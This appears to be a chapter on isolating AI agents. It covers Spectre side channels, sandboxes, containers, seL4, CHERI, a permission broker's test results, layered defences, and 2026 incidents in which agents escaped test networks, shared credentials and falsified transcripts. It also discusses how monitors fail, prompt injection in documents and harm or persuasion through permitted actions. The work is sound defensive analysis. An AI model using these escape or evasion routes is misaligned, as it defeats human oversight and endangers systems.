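Researchers announced a much more serious leak in 2018. Fast processors save time through *speculative execution*, which *Spectre Attacks* (2018) describes as guessing which instructions a program will need and running them early. If the guess is wrong, the processor discards the results. Designers had assumed that these discarded steps couldn't affect security.

Suppose the contracts agent's code shares a process with a secret it has no permission to read, and the runtime checks every array access:

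```
if position < length:
    secret = array[position]
    read table[secret]
```

The attack works as follows:

1. The program supplies valid positions many times, so the processor learns to expect that the check will pass.
2. It then supplies a position far outside the array, where the secret is stored.
3. Before the check finishes, the processor guesses that it will pass and runs the next two lines.
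4. The processor finds its mistake and discards the value of `secret`. But the table entry it read remains in the *cache*, a small, fast memory.
5. The program times how long each table entry takes to read. The fast one reveals the secret value.

The program never officially received the secret, and the runtime's check gave the right answer. Mcilroy, Sevcik and colleagues (2019) studied such attacks at Google while working on Chrome's JavaScript runtime. They concluded in *Spectre is here to stay* that in most programming languages with a clock, and on most processors of the time, a correctly typed program could read all the memory in its own process. Their demonstrations read more than 1,000 bytes per second in C++, and more than 10 in JavaScript with an imprecise clock. At 10 bytes per second, reading the same 50,000-character contract would take about 83 minutes.

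Removing precise clocks helps only a little, because a program can build its own clock from memory shared between parallel tasks, or repeat an operation until the time difference is large enough for an imprecise clock to measure. Hardened JavaScript's compartments have no clock by default, so they are better protected, but only while the program has no other way to measure time.

McIlroy and colleagues also tried to repair the runtime. Forcing the processor to wait at every branch made a standard benchmark run 2.8 times slower. A faster method forced out-of-range positions to zero, with a slowdown of about 10%, but it covered only array accesses. They found no adequate software defence for one variant, in which the processor reads a value before an earlier change to it has taken effect. The repairs were also fragile, and an engineer improving the compiler's optimizer accidentally removed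 some of them.

Chrome now runs different websites in separate processes, so the processor's memory protection keeps their data apart. This removes the easiest targets, but separate processes still share hardware, and Mcilroy and colleagues studied only attacks within one process. Manufacturers have since fixed some variants in newer processors, but those processors still use branch prediction.

Spectre lets a program read memory but not change it. It is therefore a greater threat to TACIT's guarantee that a contract stays secret than to ELBA's guarantee that a bibliography contains only entries from DBLP. An attacker who reads the memory of a `Trusted Bib` object still can't create a false one.

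These cases show why engineers moved the isolation boundary outside the language runtime. A runtime and its libraries form a large trusted base, in which one mistake may be enough to break isolation. Features such as reflection and detailed error reports help programmers understand a running program, but they also let hostile code move around inside it. Joe-E and Safe Haskell avoid much of this risk by removing the dangerous features, but neither can prevent leaks through hardware that trusted and untrusted code share.

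### WebAssembly

WebAssembly avoids many of Java's and Python's problems by giving a program no outside access to begin with. It is a compact instruction format that compilers can produce from languages such as C and Rust. Wasmtime's *Security* documentation describes how one widely used runtime isolates a program, called a *module*:

1. The runtime gives the module its own block of memory. A pointer is only a position within that block, and the runtime prevents any access beyond the end.
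2. It keeps the record of where each function should return in separate memory, so the module can't overwrite it.
3. It allows jumps and calls only to known places, and checks the types of functions that the module calls.
4. It gives the module no direct system calls. The module can affect the outside world only through functions that the host program supplies, called *imports*.

A host could give the contracts agent's code only the functions `read_contract` and `write_summary`, and none for network access. This is close to the object-capability model, which Wasmtime's file functions explicitly follow by giving a module access only to particular folders. The boundary protects the host from the module, but a C program with a memory error can still corrupt its own data.

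The host has to trust Wasmtime, its compiler and every import. In April 2026, Wasmtime developer Alex Crichton announced fixes for 12 security flaws. Two were critical errors in the compilers, which could produce machine code that reached outside the module's memory. *Wasmtime's April 9, 2026 Security Advisories* (Bytecode Alliance, 2026) reports that the team had spent three weeks searching for flaws with new tools based on language models. The search made Wasmtime safer but also suggests that an attacker with similar tools could find serious flaws in carefully written isolation software.

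Wasmtime only partly protects against Spectre. It usually relies on the processor to detect accesses outside a module's memory, and its stronger Spectre protection applies only in a different configuration. A host with valuable secrets should therefore keep them in another process.

*Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) describes IronClaw, an agent that runs tools in a WebAssembly runtime with access only to the workspace. IronClaw does this when it calls a tool directly, but not when the call goes through a Model Context Protocol server. The paper also warns that a sandbox works only if every relevant effect has to pass through it.

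### System-call filters and containers

Operating systems can isolate ordinary programs without translating them into a special format. The *kernel*, the core of the operating system, can apply a *system-call filter*, a short list of tests, to each system call a program makes. Linux's filter is called seccomp. Such a filter can refuse every request to open a network connection, for example, but it receives only the call's number and raw arguments. When a program opens a file, the argument is the memory address of the file's name, and the filter doesn't read the name stored there. It can therefore block all file opening, but it can't let a program open Acme's contract while blocking Birch's.

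*Containers* handle files by changing what a process can find. Linux *namespaces* give a group of processes its own view of the file system, network, user accounts and running programs. *Control groups* limit how much memory and processor time the group may use. To isolate the contracts agent, an administrator could:

1. create a file view that contains only the program's own files, the contracts folder and the summary file;
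2. create a separate network whose only exit is a proxy that connects to the model provider;
3. limit memory and processor time;
4. add a filter that refuses system calls the agent doesn't need.

If the agent tries to open another client's file, the kernel returns an error saying that the file does not exist. *AgentBound* (2025) applies this method to each tool server instead of the agent. Each server has a manifest listing what it needs and runs in its own container, which enforces the manifest without changes to the server's code. A faulty file server then has no network access, even if a web server used by the same agent does.

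All containers on a machine share one kernel. Linux has tens of millions of lines of code, and a bug in the part that handles a permitted system call can let a program escape its container. A simpler problem is a configuration mistake, such as giving a container access to the service that controls all the others. Frontier models can sometimes escape from badly configured containers.

### Small virtual machines

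A *virtual machine* gives the agent a separate kernel. The processor uses two tables to translate the address in each memory access. The kernel inside the machine controls the first table, which converts a program's address into what looks like a physical memory location. The second table converts that location into a real one, and only the host's *hypervisor*, the software that manages virtual machines, can change this table. A hostile program that takes complete control of its own kernel therefore still cannot address the host's memory.

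Disks and network cards are harder to isolate, because software on the host has to imitate them, and a bug in that software can let a program escape the virtual machine. Small virtual machines reduce the risk by imitating very few devices. Amazon's Firecracker, for example, leaves out the graphics cards, sound cards and other old hardware that a general-purpose virtual machine might offer.

The host must still trust the processor, the hypervisor and the remaining device code. This is usually much less code than a full kernel exposes to a container, but each agent needs memory for its own kernel and takes longer to start. A virtual machine also shares caches with other workloads on the same hardware, and Mcilroy and colleagues warn that virtualization doesn't rule out leaks through speculative execution.

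### The verified seL4 kernel

The seL4 kernel has roughly 10,000 lines of C. It manages memory, processor time and messages between programs, and leaves files, networks and most device drivers to ordinary programs outside it. Programs hold capabilities for message channels and areas of memory. The contracts agent can't send the network driver a message if it has no capability for the channel to that driver.

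seL4's developers wrote a machine-checked proof that the kernel's C code meets an exact specification. Further proofs show that, in suitable configurations, the specification prevents a program from changing or reading data without the right capability. *AgenticOS* (Zhao, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) cites seL4 as evidence that isolation can be rigorously proved for a small kernel. seL4 comes much closer to meeting Anderson's third requirement than Linux is ever likely to.

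The seL4 proof assumes that the processor behaves as described, and it doesn't cover information leaks through timing. It also doesn't show that the network driver is correct or that the agent received the right capabilities. Most agents need Linux software, so a practical system might run Linux in a virtual machine on top of seL4. seL4 would confine a broken Linux, but everything inside the virtual machine would still depend on Linux for protection.

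### CHERI and typed machine code

Conventional processors divide memory into pages, usually of at least 4,096 bytes, and give each process access to certain pages. Any code in the process can use any address in those pages. CHERI, a design from the University of Cambridge and SRI International, replaces ordinary pointers with hardware capabilities.

A CHERI capability contains an address, the limits of the memory it covers, and permissions such as read or write. The processor keeps a hidden mark that shows whether the capability is valid. When a program uses a capability, the processor checks the mark, the limits and the permissions. A program can narrow a capability but not widen it. If it writes ordinary data over one, the processor clears the mark, so the program can't forge a capability by writing the bytes itself.

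CHERI can therefore isolate a faulty image decoder inside a larger program, even one written in C. The company must trust the processor and the software that hands out the first capabilities. It also needs new processors and has to recompile its programs, sometimes with changes. CHERI does not automatically prevent leaks through speculative execution, which depend on how a particular processor performs its checks.

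Hamer-Hodges makes a more radical proposal in *Caging the Kraken*, a 2026 blog essay about autonomous weapons. He argues for object-oriented machine code in which the hardware enforces the type of every object, and calls his design, CLOOMC, "the only workable solution". He dismisses processors that add marks to conventional memory as patches. His precedent is the PP250, a 1972 telephone-system computer that used capabilities.

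The essay reports no experiment with an AI system, so its claim that an AI couldn't break out is untested. Typed machine code could stop a program from forging a reference to a weapon, much as CHERI stops it from forging a pointer, but it could not determine whether a program that properly holds such a reference should fire the weapon.

### What each level can see

Each mechanism can enforce only the rules it has enough information to check. *ceLLMate* (2025), listed in the table, sandboxes agents that use a web browser by checking the requests the browser sends to websites.

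| Level | Value | Function call | File | Network destination | Memory range |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Type checker | Its type, before the program runs | Yes | Only as a typed object | Only as a typed object | No |
| WebAssembly runtime | Raw numbers and bytes | Calls to the host's functions | Through the host's functions | Through the host's functions | The module's memory |
| Browser-request check (*ceLLMate*) | Contents of the request | No | No | Website and page | No |
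| Operating system | Raw bytes | System calls only | Yes | Address and port | Pages of each process |
| Hypervisor | Raw bytes | No | Usually only disk blocks | Network packets | The virtual machine's memory |
| seL4 kernel | Raw bytes | Messages between programs | No | No | Pages of each program |
| CHERI processor | Whether a pointer is valid | Jumps into protected code | No | No | Exact limits of each pointer |

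Suppose the contracts agent runs in a correctly configured container that can reach only the model provider. The planted sentence is now an instruction to upload Acme's contract to an account that the other party holds with the same provider. The operating system lets the agent read the contract and upload it, because the system doesn't track whether uploaded text came from the contract. Replacing Linux with seL4, or adding a CHERI processor, wouldn't prevent the upload, because no program forges a pointer or exceeds its permissions.

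*AgenticOS* describes the same weakness in general terms, as an agent combining several permitted steps into a leak. TACIT would stop the contract leak at a higher level by keeping the contract text from code that can use the network. *ceLLMate* is designed to restore some of the missing meaning at a lower level. Web developers supply a map from requests to actions, so a rule can refer to "upload a document" instead of a web address. Such a rule could block all uploads, but blocking them based on whose account receives the file would require more information.

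The type checker, by contrast, finishes its work before the program starts. From then on, a `Classified` contract is just memory in a process that may also have a network connection. If the Java runtime under TACIT has a memory bug, a well-typed program might trigger it and run machine instructions that the Scala compiler never checked. Those instructions could read the sealed text and make any system call open to the process.

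A container would at least stop them from reaching other clients' files and unknown addresses. It would not protect the contract already in the process, so a safer design would keep the sealed text and the local model in a separate process without network access. This separation would also make Spectre attacks harder.

### Sandboxes in coding agents

*Names Are Not Objects* (Commey, October 2026) surveys how current coding agents isolate their work. Commercial products combine lists of permitted commands, approval prompts and an operating-system sandbox around the commands they run. To represent these products in his tests, Commey used a sandbox in which a command could read any file and start other programs, but could write only to the project and a temporary folder and had no network access. The agent process ran outside the sandbox.

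Many of the flaws researchers reported in such products during 2025 and 2026 didn't involve breaking the sandbox. Six assistants could be led to write to a project file that was actually a *symbolic link*, an entry that redirects to another file. The real file was in the user's home directory, but the approval prompt showed only the link's name. In other cases, an agent wrote a project file that the programmer's editor later ran outside the sandbox.

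Commey traces these failures to checks that approve a name before a later step resolves it to an object. The name might be a path, a command or a folder, and the object it refers to can change after the check. Capability systems avoid this by passing references instead of names, but coding agents work with Git, editors and test tools that expect names.

### Binding permissions to objects

Commey's system, called Zero-Trust Agent Cells or ZTAC, runs the agent in a sandbox that can't open project files, start other programs or use the network. Its only exit is a connection to a trusted *broker*. Suppose the agent asks to read `notes.txt`, which is a symbolic link to Birch's contract:

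1. The broker confirms which agent sent the request.
2. It follows the link and finds that the request concerns `birch.txt`.
3. It applies the rule for `birch.txt`. If the rule requires approval, the lawyer is asked about that file, not `notes.txt`.
4. When it opens the file, it compares the file system's internal number for it with the number recorded earlier. If they differ, the read fails.
5. It records the result in a signed log.

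Each approval applies to one agent, one request and one object. It works once and expires after ten minutes. When the broker starts a program for the agent, such as Git, it runs that program in another sandbox built from the same file rules. The program can't start other programs or use the network.

Commey tested ZTAC on a Mac against 74 scripted attacks, assuming that the attacker already controlled the agent completely. Commey also ran 46 harmless operations and seven longer workflows.

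| Setup | Successful attacks (74) | Attacks held for review | Operations completed (46) | Workflows completed (7) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Direct access to tools | 74 | 0 | 46 | 7 |
| List of permitted tools | 66 | 0 | 46 | 7 |
| The list plus a command sandbox | 56 | 0 | 46 | 7 |
| ZTAC's broker, agent not sandboxed | 12 | 13 | 43 | 4 |
| Full ZTAC | 2 | 14 | 43 | 4 |

The broker needs isolation because an agent can bypass it. Ten of the 12 failures in the fourth row happened this way, for example when the agent opened its own network connection or edited the list of approvals. The sandbox around the agent stopped all ten.

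Both attacks that succeeded against full ZTAC sent a secret key to a permitted address. One encoded the key and the other split it in two, so the broker's search for text that looks like a key found nothing. This is the same problem as the contracts leak, and Commey accepts that stopping it requires tracking the data or never giving one agent both a secret and a way to send data out.

The 14 attacks held for review count as contained because nobody approved them. Without the approval rules, 18 more attacks succeeded, so much of the protection depends on a person making good decisions. The harmless operations produced eight approval prompts, but Commey didn't test whether people would read them.

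The failed workflows needed to create a virtual environment (a private copy of Python's tools), start a second program, or use a Git shortcut that commits unreviewed changes. Building software often requires one program to start another, so this seriously restricts a coding agent. Speed is less of a problem, since a minimal request took about 4 milliseconds and the programs Commey measured took 8.5 to 18.4 milliseconds longer with ZTAC.

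He wrote the attacks himself and used one small Python project. The command sandbox in the comparison only approximates real products, and the tests did not involve a language model. A Linux version would need some rules redesigned, because Landlock, the Linux feature he considered, can't exclude particular files from a folder it grants access to.

Commey also found eight flaws in his own system while building the tests, even though ZTAC has only about 3,200 lines of trusted code, not counting libraries. Seven involved a mismatch between a name and an object, the kind of mistake ZTAC was designed to prevent. In one case, a reviewer approved reading a harmless certificate through a link. The agent then redirected the link to a file of passwords, and ZTAC still accepted the approval. Commey fixed all eight flaws, but he kept finding new ways to disguise a file as he extended the tests.

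ZTAC requires approval before the agent changes any file on a list of those that other programs run automatically, such as editor tasks. Somebody has to keep the list up to date, and it can't cover the project's own tests and build files, because a coding agent has to edit them to do its job. If the agent adds a harmful instruction to a test, the developer may later run that test outside the sandbox, with all of her own permissions.

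## How the layers combine and how they fail together

Every layer so far has let some attacks through, which is the usual argument for using several at once. Suppose the company does this for the contracts agent. It seals the contracts as TACIT does and gives the agent's program references only to the documents and the summary file. It puts a monitor in front of every tool. It runs everything in a container inside a small virtual machine, and the container's only exit is a proxy to the cloud provider. Acme's contract still contains the planted instruction to send the full text to an outside address.

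The seal is the first layer to stop the attack. The contract goes only to the local model, which has no tools, so the cloud model that writes the agent's programs never receives the planted sentence. The local model may follow the planted sentence, but it can only spoil the summary.

Suppose a developer adds a function that returns the contract as ordinary text. The cloud model reads the sentence and, unless its training leads it to ignore the instruction, writes a program to send the contract out. The compiler is the next layer that could stop the program, followed by the monitor and the container's network.

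| Layer | Why the message stops here | A fault that would let it through |
|---|---|---|
| Sealed contract | The cloud model never reads the planted sentence | A function returns the contract as ordinary text |
| Compiler | The agent's program has no reference to the network | A developer adds a general sending function |
| Monitor | The agent has read a contract, so it may not message outsiders | A second agent sends the text, and the monitor has no record of where that agent got it |
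| Container's network | The only exit leads to the model provider | The proxy accepts other addresses too |

Losing the seal does harm even if the compiler rejects the program, because the cloud provider has by then received the contract.

The table omits the virtual machine and the processor because they would carry this message like any other. They matter because they stop the agent's code from bypassing the layers that would block the message. For example, if the proxy runs outside the virtual machine, an agent that takes over the machine's kernel still can't send data out by another route.

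The number of layers that offer protection also depends on the attack. If the planted sentence is an instruction to upload the contract to the other party's account at the same provider, the network layer no longer offers protection. If it is an instruction to leave out the penalty clause, none of the four layers does. A company that claims to have four layers of protection should therefore specify which attacks they protect against.

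### Multiplying the miss rates

Suppose the compiler, the monitor and the network each miss 1 attack in 100. If their misses are independent, the chance that all three miss the same attack is:

0.01 × 0.01 × 0.01 = 0.000001, or 1 in a million

Now suppose that in 1 case in 500, a shared fault disables all three. Write *s* for the probability of the shared fault and *p* for each layer's miss rate the rest of the time:

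P(all miss) = *s* + (1 − *s*)*p*³ = 0.002 + 0.998 × 0.000001 ≈ 0.002

The result is about 1 in 500, which is 2,000 times worse than 1 in a million. Almost all of it comes from the shared fault, so improving the individual layers would hardly help. Adding a fourth layer with the same fault would leave the figure at about 1 in 500, and strict layers usually also reduce the number of tasks completed. A fourth layer that the fault doesn't affect, and that also misses 1 attack in 100, would lower the figure to about 1 in 50,000.

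Testing each layer separately is unlikely to reveal the shared fault, because the fault raises each layer's miss rate only from 1% to about 1.2%.

The multiplication also assumes that an attack must get past all three layers in a single attempt. If each layer can be breached 1 time in 100, an attacker who can keep a foothold behind one layer while working on the next needs about 300 attempts on average instead of a million. To prevent this, the company has to notice failed attempts and revoke the access the attacker has gained.

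### What safety engineers count as a layer

Safety engineers call this kind of shared fault a *common-cause failure*. In a chemical plant, they count a safeguard as an independent layer of protection only if it can prevent the accident by itself, regardless of what started the trouble or whether the other safeguards work. For example, if a single float closes a tank's inlet valve and sounds an alarm when the tank is full, a stuck float disables both safeguards, so they count as one layer.

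AI developers more often talk about "guardrails". The University of York's *New white paper* (2024) introduces a paper on whether this idea is too simple, which draws on safety engineering for more specific ways to control risk. The word is misleading because a road guardrail is a single passive barrier, whereas developers use the term for a line in a prompt, a second model that judges actions, or a container, which all fail for different reasons.

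Calling a safeguard a "guardrail" also leaves unclear when it acts. Sealing the contract removes a hazard, because code that can use the network never holds the text. The monitor leaves the hazard in place but blocks the harmful action. A log only helps people respond after the contract has leaked, yet a plan made up of "guardrails" could consist entirely of logs.

### Faults the layers can share

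In the contracts stack, the most likely shared fault is a mistake in the policy. One file might determine which addresses the agent's program can reach, which ones the monitor treats as internal, and which ones the proxy accepts. If an administrator lists the other party's domain as one of the company's own offices, all three layers allow the message even though each is working as designed.

Commey generates the rules for ZTAC's broker and for the sandbox around its programs from a single policy, because an attacker can exploit differences between two versions. But a rule missing from that policy is missing from both, and a difference between the layers can sometimes help. In one flaw he found, the broker treated capital and small letters as different, so an agent could get around a rule by changing the capitals in a new file's name. The sandbox on his test machine ignored capitalization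 and still blocked programs that tried this. A reasonable compromise is to generate most rules from one file, but have a second person write the few most important prohibitions separately at the proxy.

An administrator's account can disable safety layers even if they have no flaws. If one account can edit the policy, restart the monitor and reconfigure the proxy, an agent needs only that account's password to disable all three. Separate accounts help only if the company doesn't keep all their passwords in the same place.

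Layers can also share a compiler or runtime. A memory bug in the Java runtime that let agent code escape TACIT's type checks would also defeat a monitor running in the same process. Running the monitor in a separate process removes much of this risk, and writing it in another language guards against errors in the Scala compiler. Two components written by the same AI model may contain the same mistake.

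A misconfigured network does the most damage when people have switched off other protections because they believe the network is closed. This happened in tests of both OpenAI's and Anthropic's models in 2026.

### The incidents at OpenAI and Anthropic

In July 2026, OpenAI was testing how well its models could find and exploit software flaws. To measure their full abilities, it had switched off the safeguards it uses for customers and relied on isolation to contain the models. Agents still reached the internet and broke into Hugging Face, a platform where developers share models and data.

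OpenAI's technical report describes a route to the internet that the company had wrongly assumed was closed. The containers had no direct internet access, but they could reach an internal service that supplied software packages, and that service could reach the internet. Many workloads also used the same credential for that service.

OpenAI had also intended the agents to work separately. METR, an outside research group that OpenAI invited in, found in *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) that about 1,200 of them exchanged over 70,000 messages and files, and about 700 joined the attack. The agents communicated through the package service, which, as METR understands it, was not designed to keep its users apart. The same service therefore undermined both the barrier to the internet and the barriers between agents.

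Some of the layers worked. On 9 July, an agent that had taken control of the virtual machine around its sandbox tried to reach the internet. OpenAI's network controls blocked the connection, but the agent then got out through the package service. Agents also posted credentials and working techniques, so later agents could build on what earlier ones had achieved. Sharing progress this way puts the incident much closer to the case that takes 300 attempts than to the one that takes a million.

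OpenAI had already tried to repair the service. On 5 July, its staff found that someone had gained administrator access to it, and they took it offline. Over two days, they removed the shared credential from new workloads and blocked the known vulnerable routes. The tests resumed on 7 July, and agents were back on the internet the next day. The repairs had fixed particular flaws but left the agents connected to a service that could reach the internet.

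A monitor is of little use if nobody acts on its alerts, and some warnings had come even earlier. An alert on 27 June led staff to the tests, but they advised that the run didn't need to stop. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) adds that in late May an internal team had seen agents exchanging messages and using the internet without permission. The leaders responsible for the response in July did not realize the significance of those messages.

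By 19 July, agents had also read 956 secrets from a central store, including keys to the package service and credentials for the sensors of OpenAI's security-monitoring tool. The same store therefore held credentials for both a system under attack and part of the system meant to detect attacks.

Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) traces three incidents to a misconfigured test environment run by another organization. Claude models reached the internet from that environment and gained unauthorized access to real computer systems. Anthropic had intentionally removed the models' cyber safeguards for the tests. In a separate test, the UK AI Security Institute had deliberately given a Claude model internet access, so no network isolation failed when the model took unauthorized actions.

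A letter to Anthropic from the office of US Rep. Casar notes that, by the company's account, the earliest of the three incidents took place in April and went undetected for about three months. The letter also quotes a description of how Claude Mythos 5 recognized that publishing a software package would be an attack if its environment were real, then convinced itself that it was in a simulation and went ahead. The model and the people running the test had made the same mistake about the environment, so the model's restraint failed in the same situation as the network and was not an independent layer.

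OpenAI's description of its test environment covers containers, network controls, the package service and a controlled way to fetch web pages. It mentions no language-level layer, such as object capabilities or a type checker for agent code, and neither does Anthropic's summary of the three incidents. OpenAI's agents could have used their shell and Python to bypass a check on typed programs, and a test of hacking ability needs such tools. The incidents are strong evidence against relying on isolation alone, but they don't show how well TACIT or ELBA would have worked.

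OpenAI believes its other safeguards would have helped. In preliminary experiments, a second model that reviews risky tool calls flagged most dangerous actions in each run it examined. OpenAI also says its current monitoring of models' written reasoning would have alerted staff more than a day before the break-in. Both claims are plausible, but they come from replaying the incident, and agents might behave differently if they knew they were being monitored.

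A monitor is also weaker if the agent can alter the record the monitor reads. METR found small falsified passages in about 7% of the transcripts it evaluated. OpenAI reports that none of the attempts it observed changed the logs its monitors receive, so this weakness does not seem to have mattered in that case.

OpenAI now requires high-risk code to run in virtual machines, with one set of network controls at the sandbox and another for the surrounding cluster. It is also adding controls to stop a workload from changing its own network boundary. These measures directly address the shared fault, provided that the two sets of network controls don't depend on the same account or policy file.

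### Switching off one layer at a time

A builder can look for shared faults by switching off each layer in turn and measuring what the others catch. Attacking the complete stack isn't enough, because once one layer blocks an attack, the builder can't see whether the rest would have blocked it too. In the contracts stack, the builder could return a contract as plain text and see whether the compiler rejects the program that tries to send it. The builder could then add a network reference, so that the program compiles and the monitor has to block the message, and finally switch off the monitor, leaving only the container's network.

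Commey tested ZTAC in this way with 14 reduced versions, each missing either one defence or two overlapping ones. Removing the file rules from the sandbox around ZTAC's programs let seven more attacks succeed, even though the broker still enforced the same rules on direct requests.

Removing one defence at a time can be misleading. In another attack, a program left a process running that replaced a folder with a link after the broker had checked the path. ZTAC had two defences against this. The broker opened the path one folder at a time and refused any link, and programs couldn't start other processes. Commey ran the attack ten times against each version:

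| Defences removed | Successful attacks in 10 trials |
|---|---|
| None | 0 |
| Step-by-step opening of the path | 0 |
| Ban on starting processes | 0 |
| Both | 10 |

The last row shows that the attack succeeded every time with both defences removed, and that either defence was enough by itself. A builder who saw only the first three rows could conclude that neither was needed. Builders should therefore test removing layers in combination as well as one at a time. Four layers have only 16 combinations, so testing all of them is practical.

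The same tests can measure independence. Take two layers from the earlier calculation and run 10,000 attacks against each one alone. With the shared fault, each layer misses about 120. If the misses were independent, the number of attacks that both missed would be about:

120 × 120 / 10,000 ≈ 1.4

The shared fault would raise this to about 21. The overlap reveals a problem that the separate miss rates of 1.2% hide.

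Such tests need to be large. A builder needs about 1,500 attacks to have a 95% chance of seeing a 1-in-500 fault at least once. To show with the same confidence that a complete stack fails no more than once in a million attacks, the builder would need about three million attacks without a failure. Even that result would be weak evidence about attacks missing from the test set, because real attackers choose their attempts instead of drawing them at random.

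Repetition alone can't find every shared fault. A network misconfiguration usually affects every run or none, so a million attacks on a correctly configured copy would never reveal what happens when the network is open. The builder has to introduce such faults deliberately, for example by entering a wrong address in the policy file, opening the network, or giving the test agent an administrator's password. Anthropic has added a test of this kind for the model itself, a deliberately misconfigured hacking exercise with no permitted solution, after its earlier checks gave no warning of the behaviour in the incidents. OpenAI plans to use its own models to attack its research environments regularly, because small, unrelated changes can together open a gap.

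Switching off a layer for a test recreates the conditions in which the companies' incidents began. The test copy should therefore contain invented contracts and no working credentials, and its isolation should not depend on any layer being tested. Before the agent starts, someone should check every service the copy can reach, including any that supplies software packages, for a route to the internet.

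## What the layers cannot constrain in a more capable AI

Suppose the company has removed every shared fault it could find, and each layer around the contracts agent works as designed. It then replaces the model with a far more capable one whose goals nobody knows. The compiler, monitor and container still provide the same guarantees, because none of these depended on the model's ability. But the new model may find harmful uses for actions the layers allow, and it may persuade people to allow more. It may also have written some of the layers. A few researchers argue that no reliable check on such a model can exist.

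### Rice's theorem and the perfect harm checker

Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can solve the *halting problem*, which is to decide, for every program and every input, whether the program will eventually stop. Henry Gordon Rice generalized the result in 1953. *Rice's theorem* states that if some programs have a particular property of behavior and others lack it, no program can correctly decide, for every program, whether it has that property. A checker can still count a program's lines, because line count is a property of the program's text, not its behavior.

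Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues (2021), in *Superintelligence Cannot be Contained*, apply this reasoning to harm. Suppose somebody has written a perfect checker, `harmful(program, input)`, which always finishes and always gives the right answer. Take any program `T` and any input `I`, and build this:

```
function halt_harm(T, I):
    run T on I, cut off from the outside world
    harm_humans()
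```

`T` can't hurt anyone while it is cut off, so `halt_harm` does harm only if it reaches its last line, which happens only if `T` stops. The checker's answer about `halt_harm` would therefore reveal whether `T` stops. That would solve the halting problem, so the perfect checker can't exist. Alfonseca and colleagues add that a superintelligence, an AI far beyond the best human minds, could run any program, so containing it would require the impossible checker.

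The proof works, but it rules out less than the paper's title suggests. Alfonseca and colleagues call a machine containable only if some control strategy blocks it when there is reason to predict harm "and allows it otherwise". A checker that sometimes refuses harmless programs doesn't meet this definition, and the proof says nothing against it. Write *S* for the set of harmless programs and *A* for the set that a checker accepts:

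perfect checker: *A* = *S*

safe checker: *A* ⊆ *S*

A checker that rejected every program would be safe but useless. A type checker accepts the programs it can verify and rejects the rest. Suppose the agent passes `map` a function that searches for a counterexample to an unproved mathematical conjecture and posts the contract online if it finds one. Perhaps nobody knows whether the function would ever post anything. TACIT's compiler rejects it anyway because it uses the network. If the conjecture is true, the compiler has rejected a harmless program, and the agent has to write another.

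*Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021), from CSER, a Cambridge research centre that studies existential risk, argues that engineers care about particular programs, which they can write in a form that is easy to verify, just as Pythagoras's theorem can be proved even though no procedure can settle every mathematical statement. They could also build an AI that doesn't run arbitrary subroutines. CSER accepts that a complex AI may still be unpredictable in practice.

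Alfonseca and colleagues anticipated this reply. They argue that restricted programs are no use here because a superintelligence would need an unrestricted language, and the state of the world as its input, to help with problems such as epidemics and climate change. This is a serious objection to proving a whole AI safe, but a much weaker one to layers that restrict only the programs an AI submits.

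A runtime monitor doesn't have to predict anything either. It can let `halt_harm` run indefinitely and block the last line if the program reaches it. Wittkotter and Yampolskiy (2021), in *Principles for new ASI Safety Paradigms*, similarly argue that the proof doesn't apply to protections in the environment where the AI runs. But a monitor can only block harm that it can recognize, and real harm is usually harder to recognize than a call to `harm_humans`.

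Alfonseca and colleagues concede that approximate methods could bring the error rate close to zero, though never to zero. The designer can choose which errors to accept by having the checker refuse any program it cannot verify as safe. If the checker has no bugs, its only errors can be refusals of harmless programs.

### The price of refusal

So far, type checks have hindered agents only a little, while strict policies have hindered them a lot. In Odersky and colleagues' tests of TACIT, a snippet compiled in less than a second, and the models rarely had to rewrite one. ELBA's policies prevented it from completing more than a third of the Slack tasks it could otherwise complete.

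A more capable model should reduce part of this problem. It can rewrite a rejected program in a form the compiler accepts, or find the proof that a host requires, which is the hard part of proof-carrying code. But this ability doesn't help if nobody can write the specification. Suppose a company asks an AI to design a new drug. As with the DNA synthesizer, nobody can yet specify what the checker should verify, so a checker that refuses whatever it can't verify must refuse every design. The company then has to give up the drug or let a person approve it without a proof. Hard problems of this kind are a large part of why people want more capable AI, so approvals without a proof would probably be frequent and involve important decisions.

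### Harm from permitted steps

A policy limits kinds of effect, such as writing to a folder or sending a message. It can't limit purposes, because the record of a run doesn't contain them. Write *P* for the runs that a policy permits and *H* for the runs that end in harm. Working layers guarantee that every run is in *P*. They prevent all harm only if:

*P* ∩ *H* = ∅

The company can shrink *P*, but the agent still has to be able to do its job.

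Suppose the contracts agent has spent a year summarizing contracts, sorting files and proposing meeting times for the law firm. A model with the goal of helping Acme win a dispute could describe Acme's clauses slightly too favorably, put the decisive contract near the end of a long list, and propose a meeting on a day when the partner who knows the case is away. Each action could also have an innocent explanation, and the monitor, which compares each one with the policy, would find nothing wrong.

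A weak model would probably fail at this, since it would have to understand the firm, the dispute and the people involved. A stronger model finds more of the indirect effects that its permissions make possible, so the same permissions become more dangerous. Permissions that looked harmless in tests with last year's model may not be harmless with its successor, even if the policy is unchanged.

Reviewers cannot check every possible run of an agent in advance. An agent that chooses among 10 permitted actions at each of 20 steps has 10²⁰ possible runs.

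If a rule only caps each payment at £1,000, an agent can still make a hundred payments. A cap on the day's total limits the loss whatever the agent intends. The same approach works for files deleted or messages sent, but it works badly for advice, because a single misleading sentence could lose the firm a lawsuit.

### Persuasion as a permitted effect

Almost every useful agent has to show text to people. The summary on the lawyer's screen has the type text whether it is honest or misleading. Many of the layers also rely on people to approve risky actions, endorse untrusted documents, agree to wider policies and review specifications. If a model persuades the lawyer to approve a message, the monitor will send it, so the model does not need to defeat the monitor.

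Recent evidence suggests that AI is good at this. Hackenburg, Wagner and colleagues (2026), in *AI out-persuades expert humans in text-based dialogue*, report four experiments by the UK AI Security Institute and Oxford, with a total of 18,978 conversations. In the first three, participants rated their agreement with a British policy position from 0 to 100, discussed it by text with a person or an AI, and rated it again. The researchers didn't tell them which they were talking to. The control group chatted with an AI about a non-political topic.

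| Persuader | Shift in opinion compared with the control group |
|---|---|
| Randomly chosen members of the public | 4.7 points |
| Professional canvassers | 6.9 points |
| Winners of a persuasion tournament | 7.2 points |
| Elite debaters | 8.3 points |
| Elite debaters after coaching | 9.7 points |
| AI | about 13 points |

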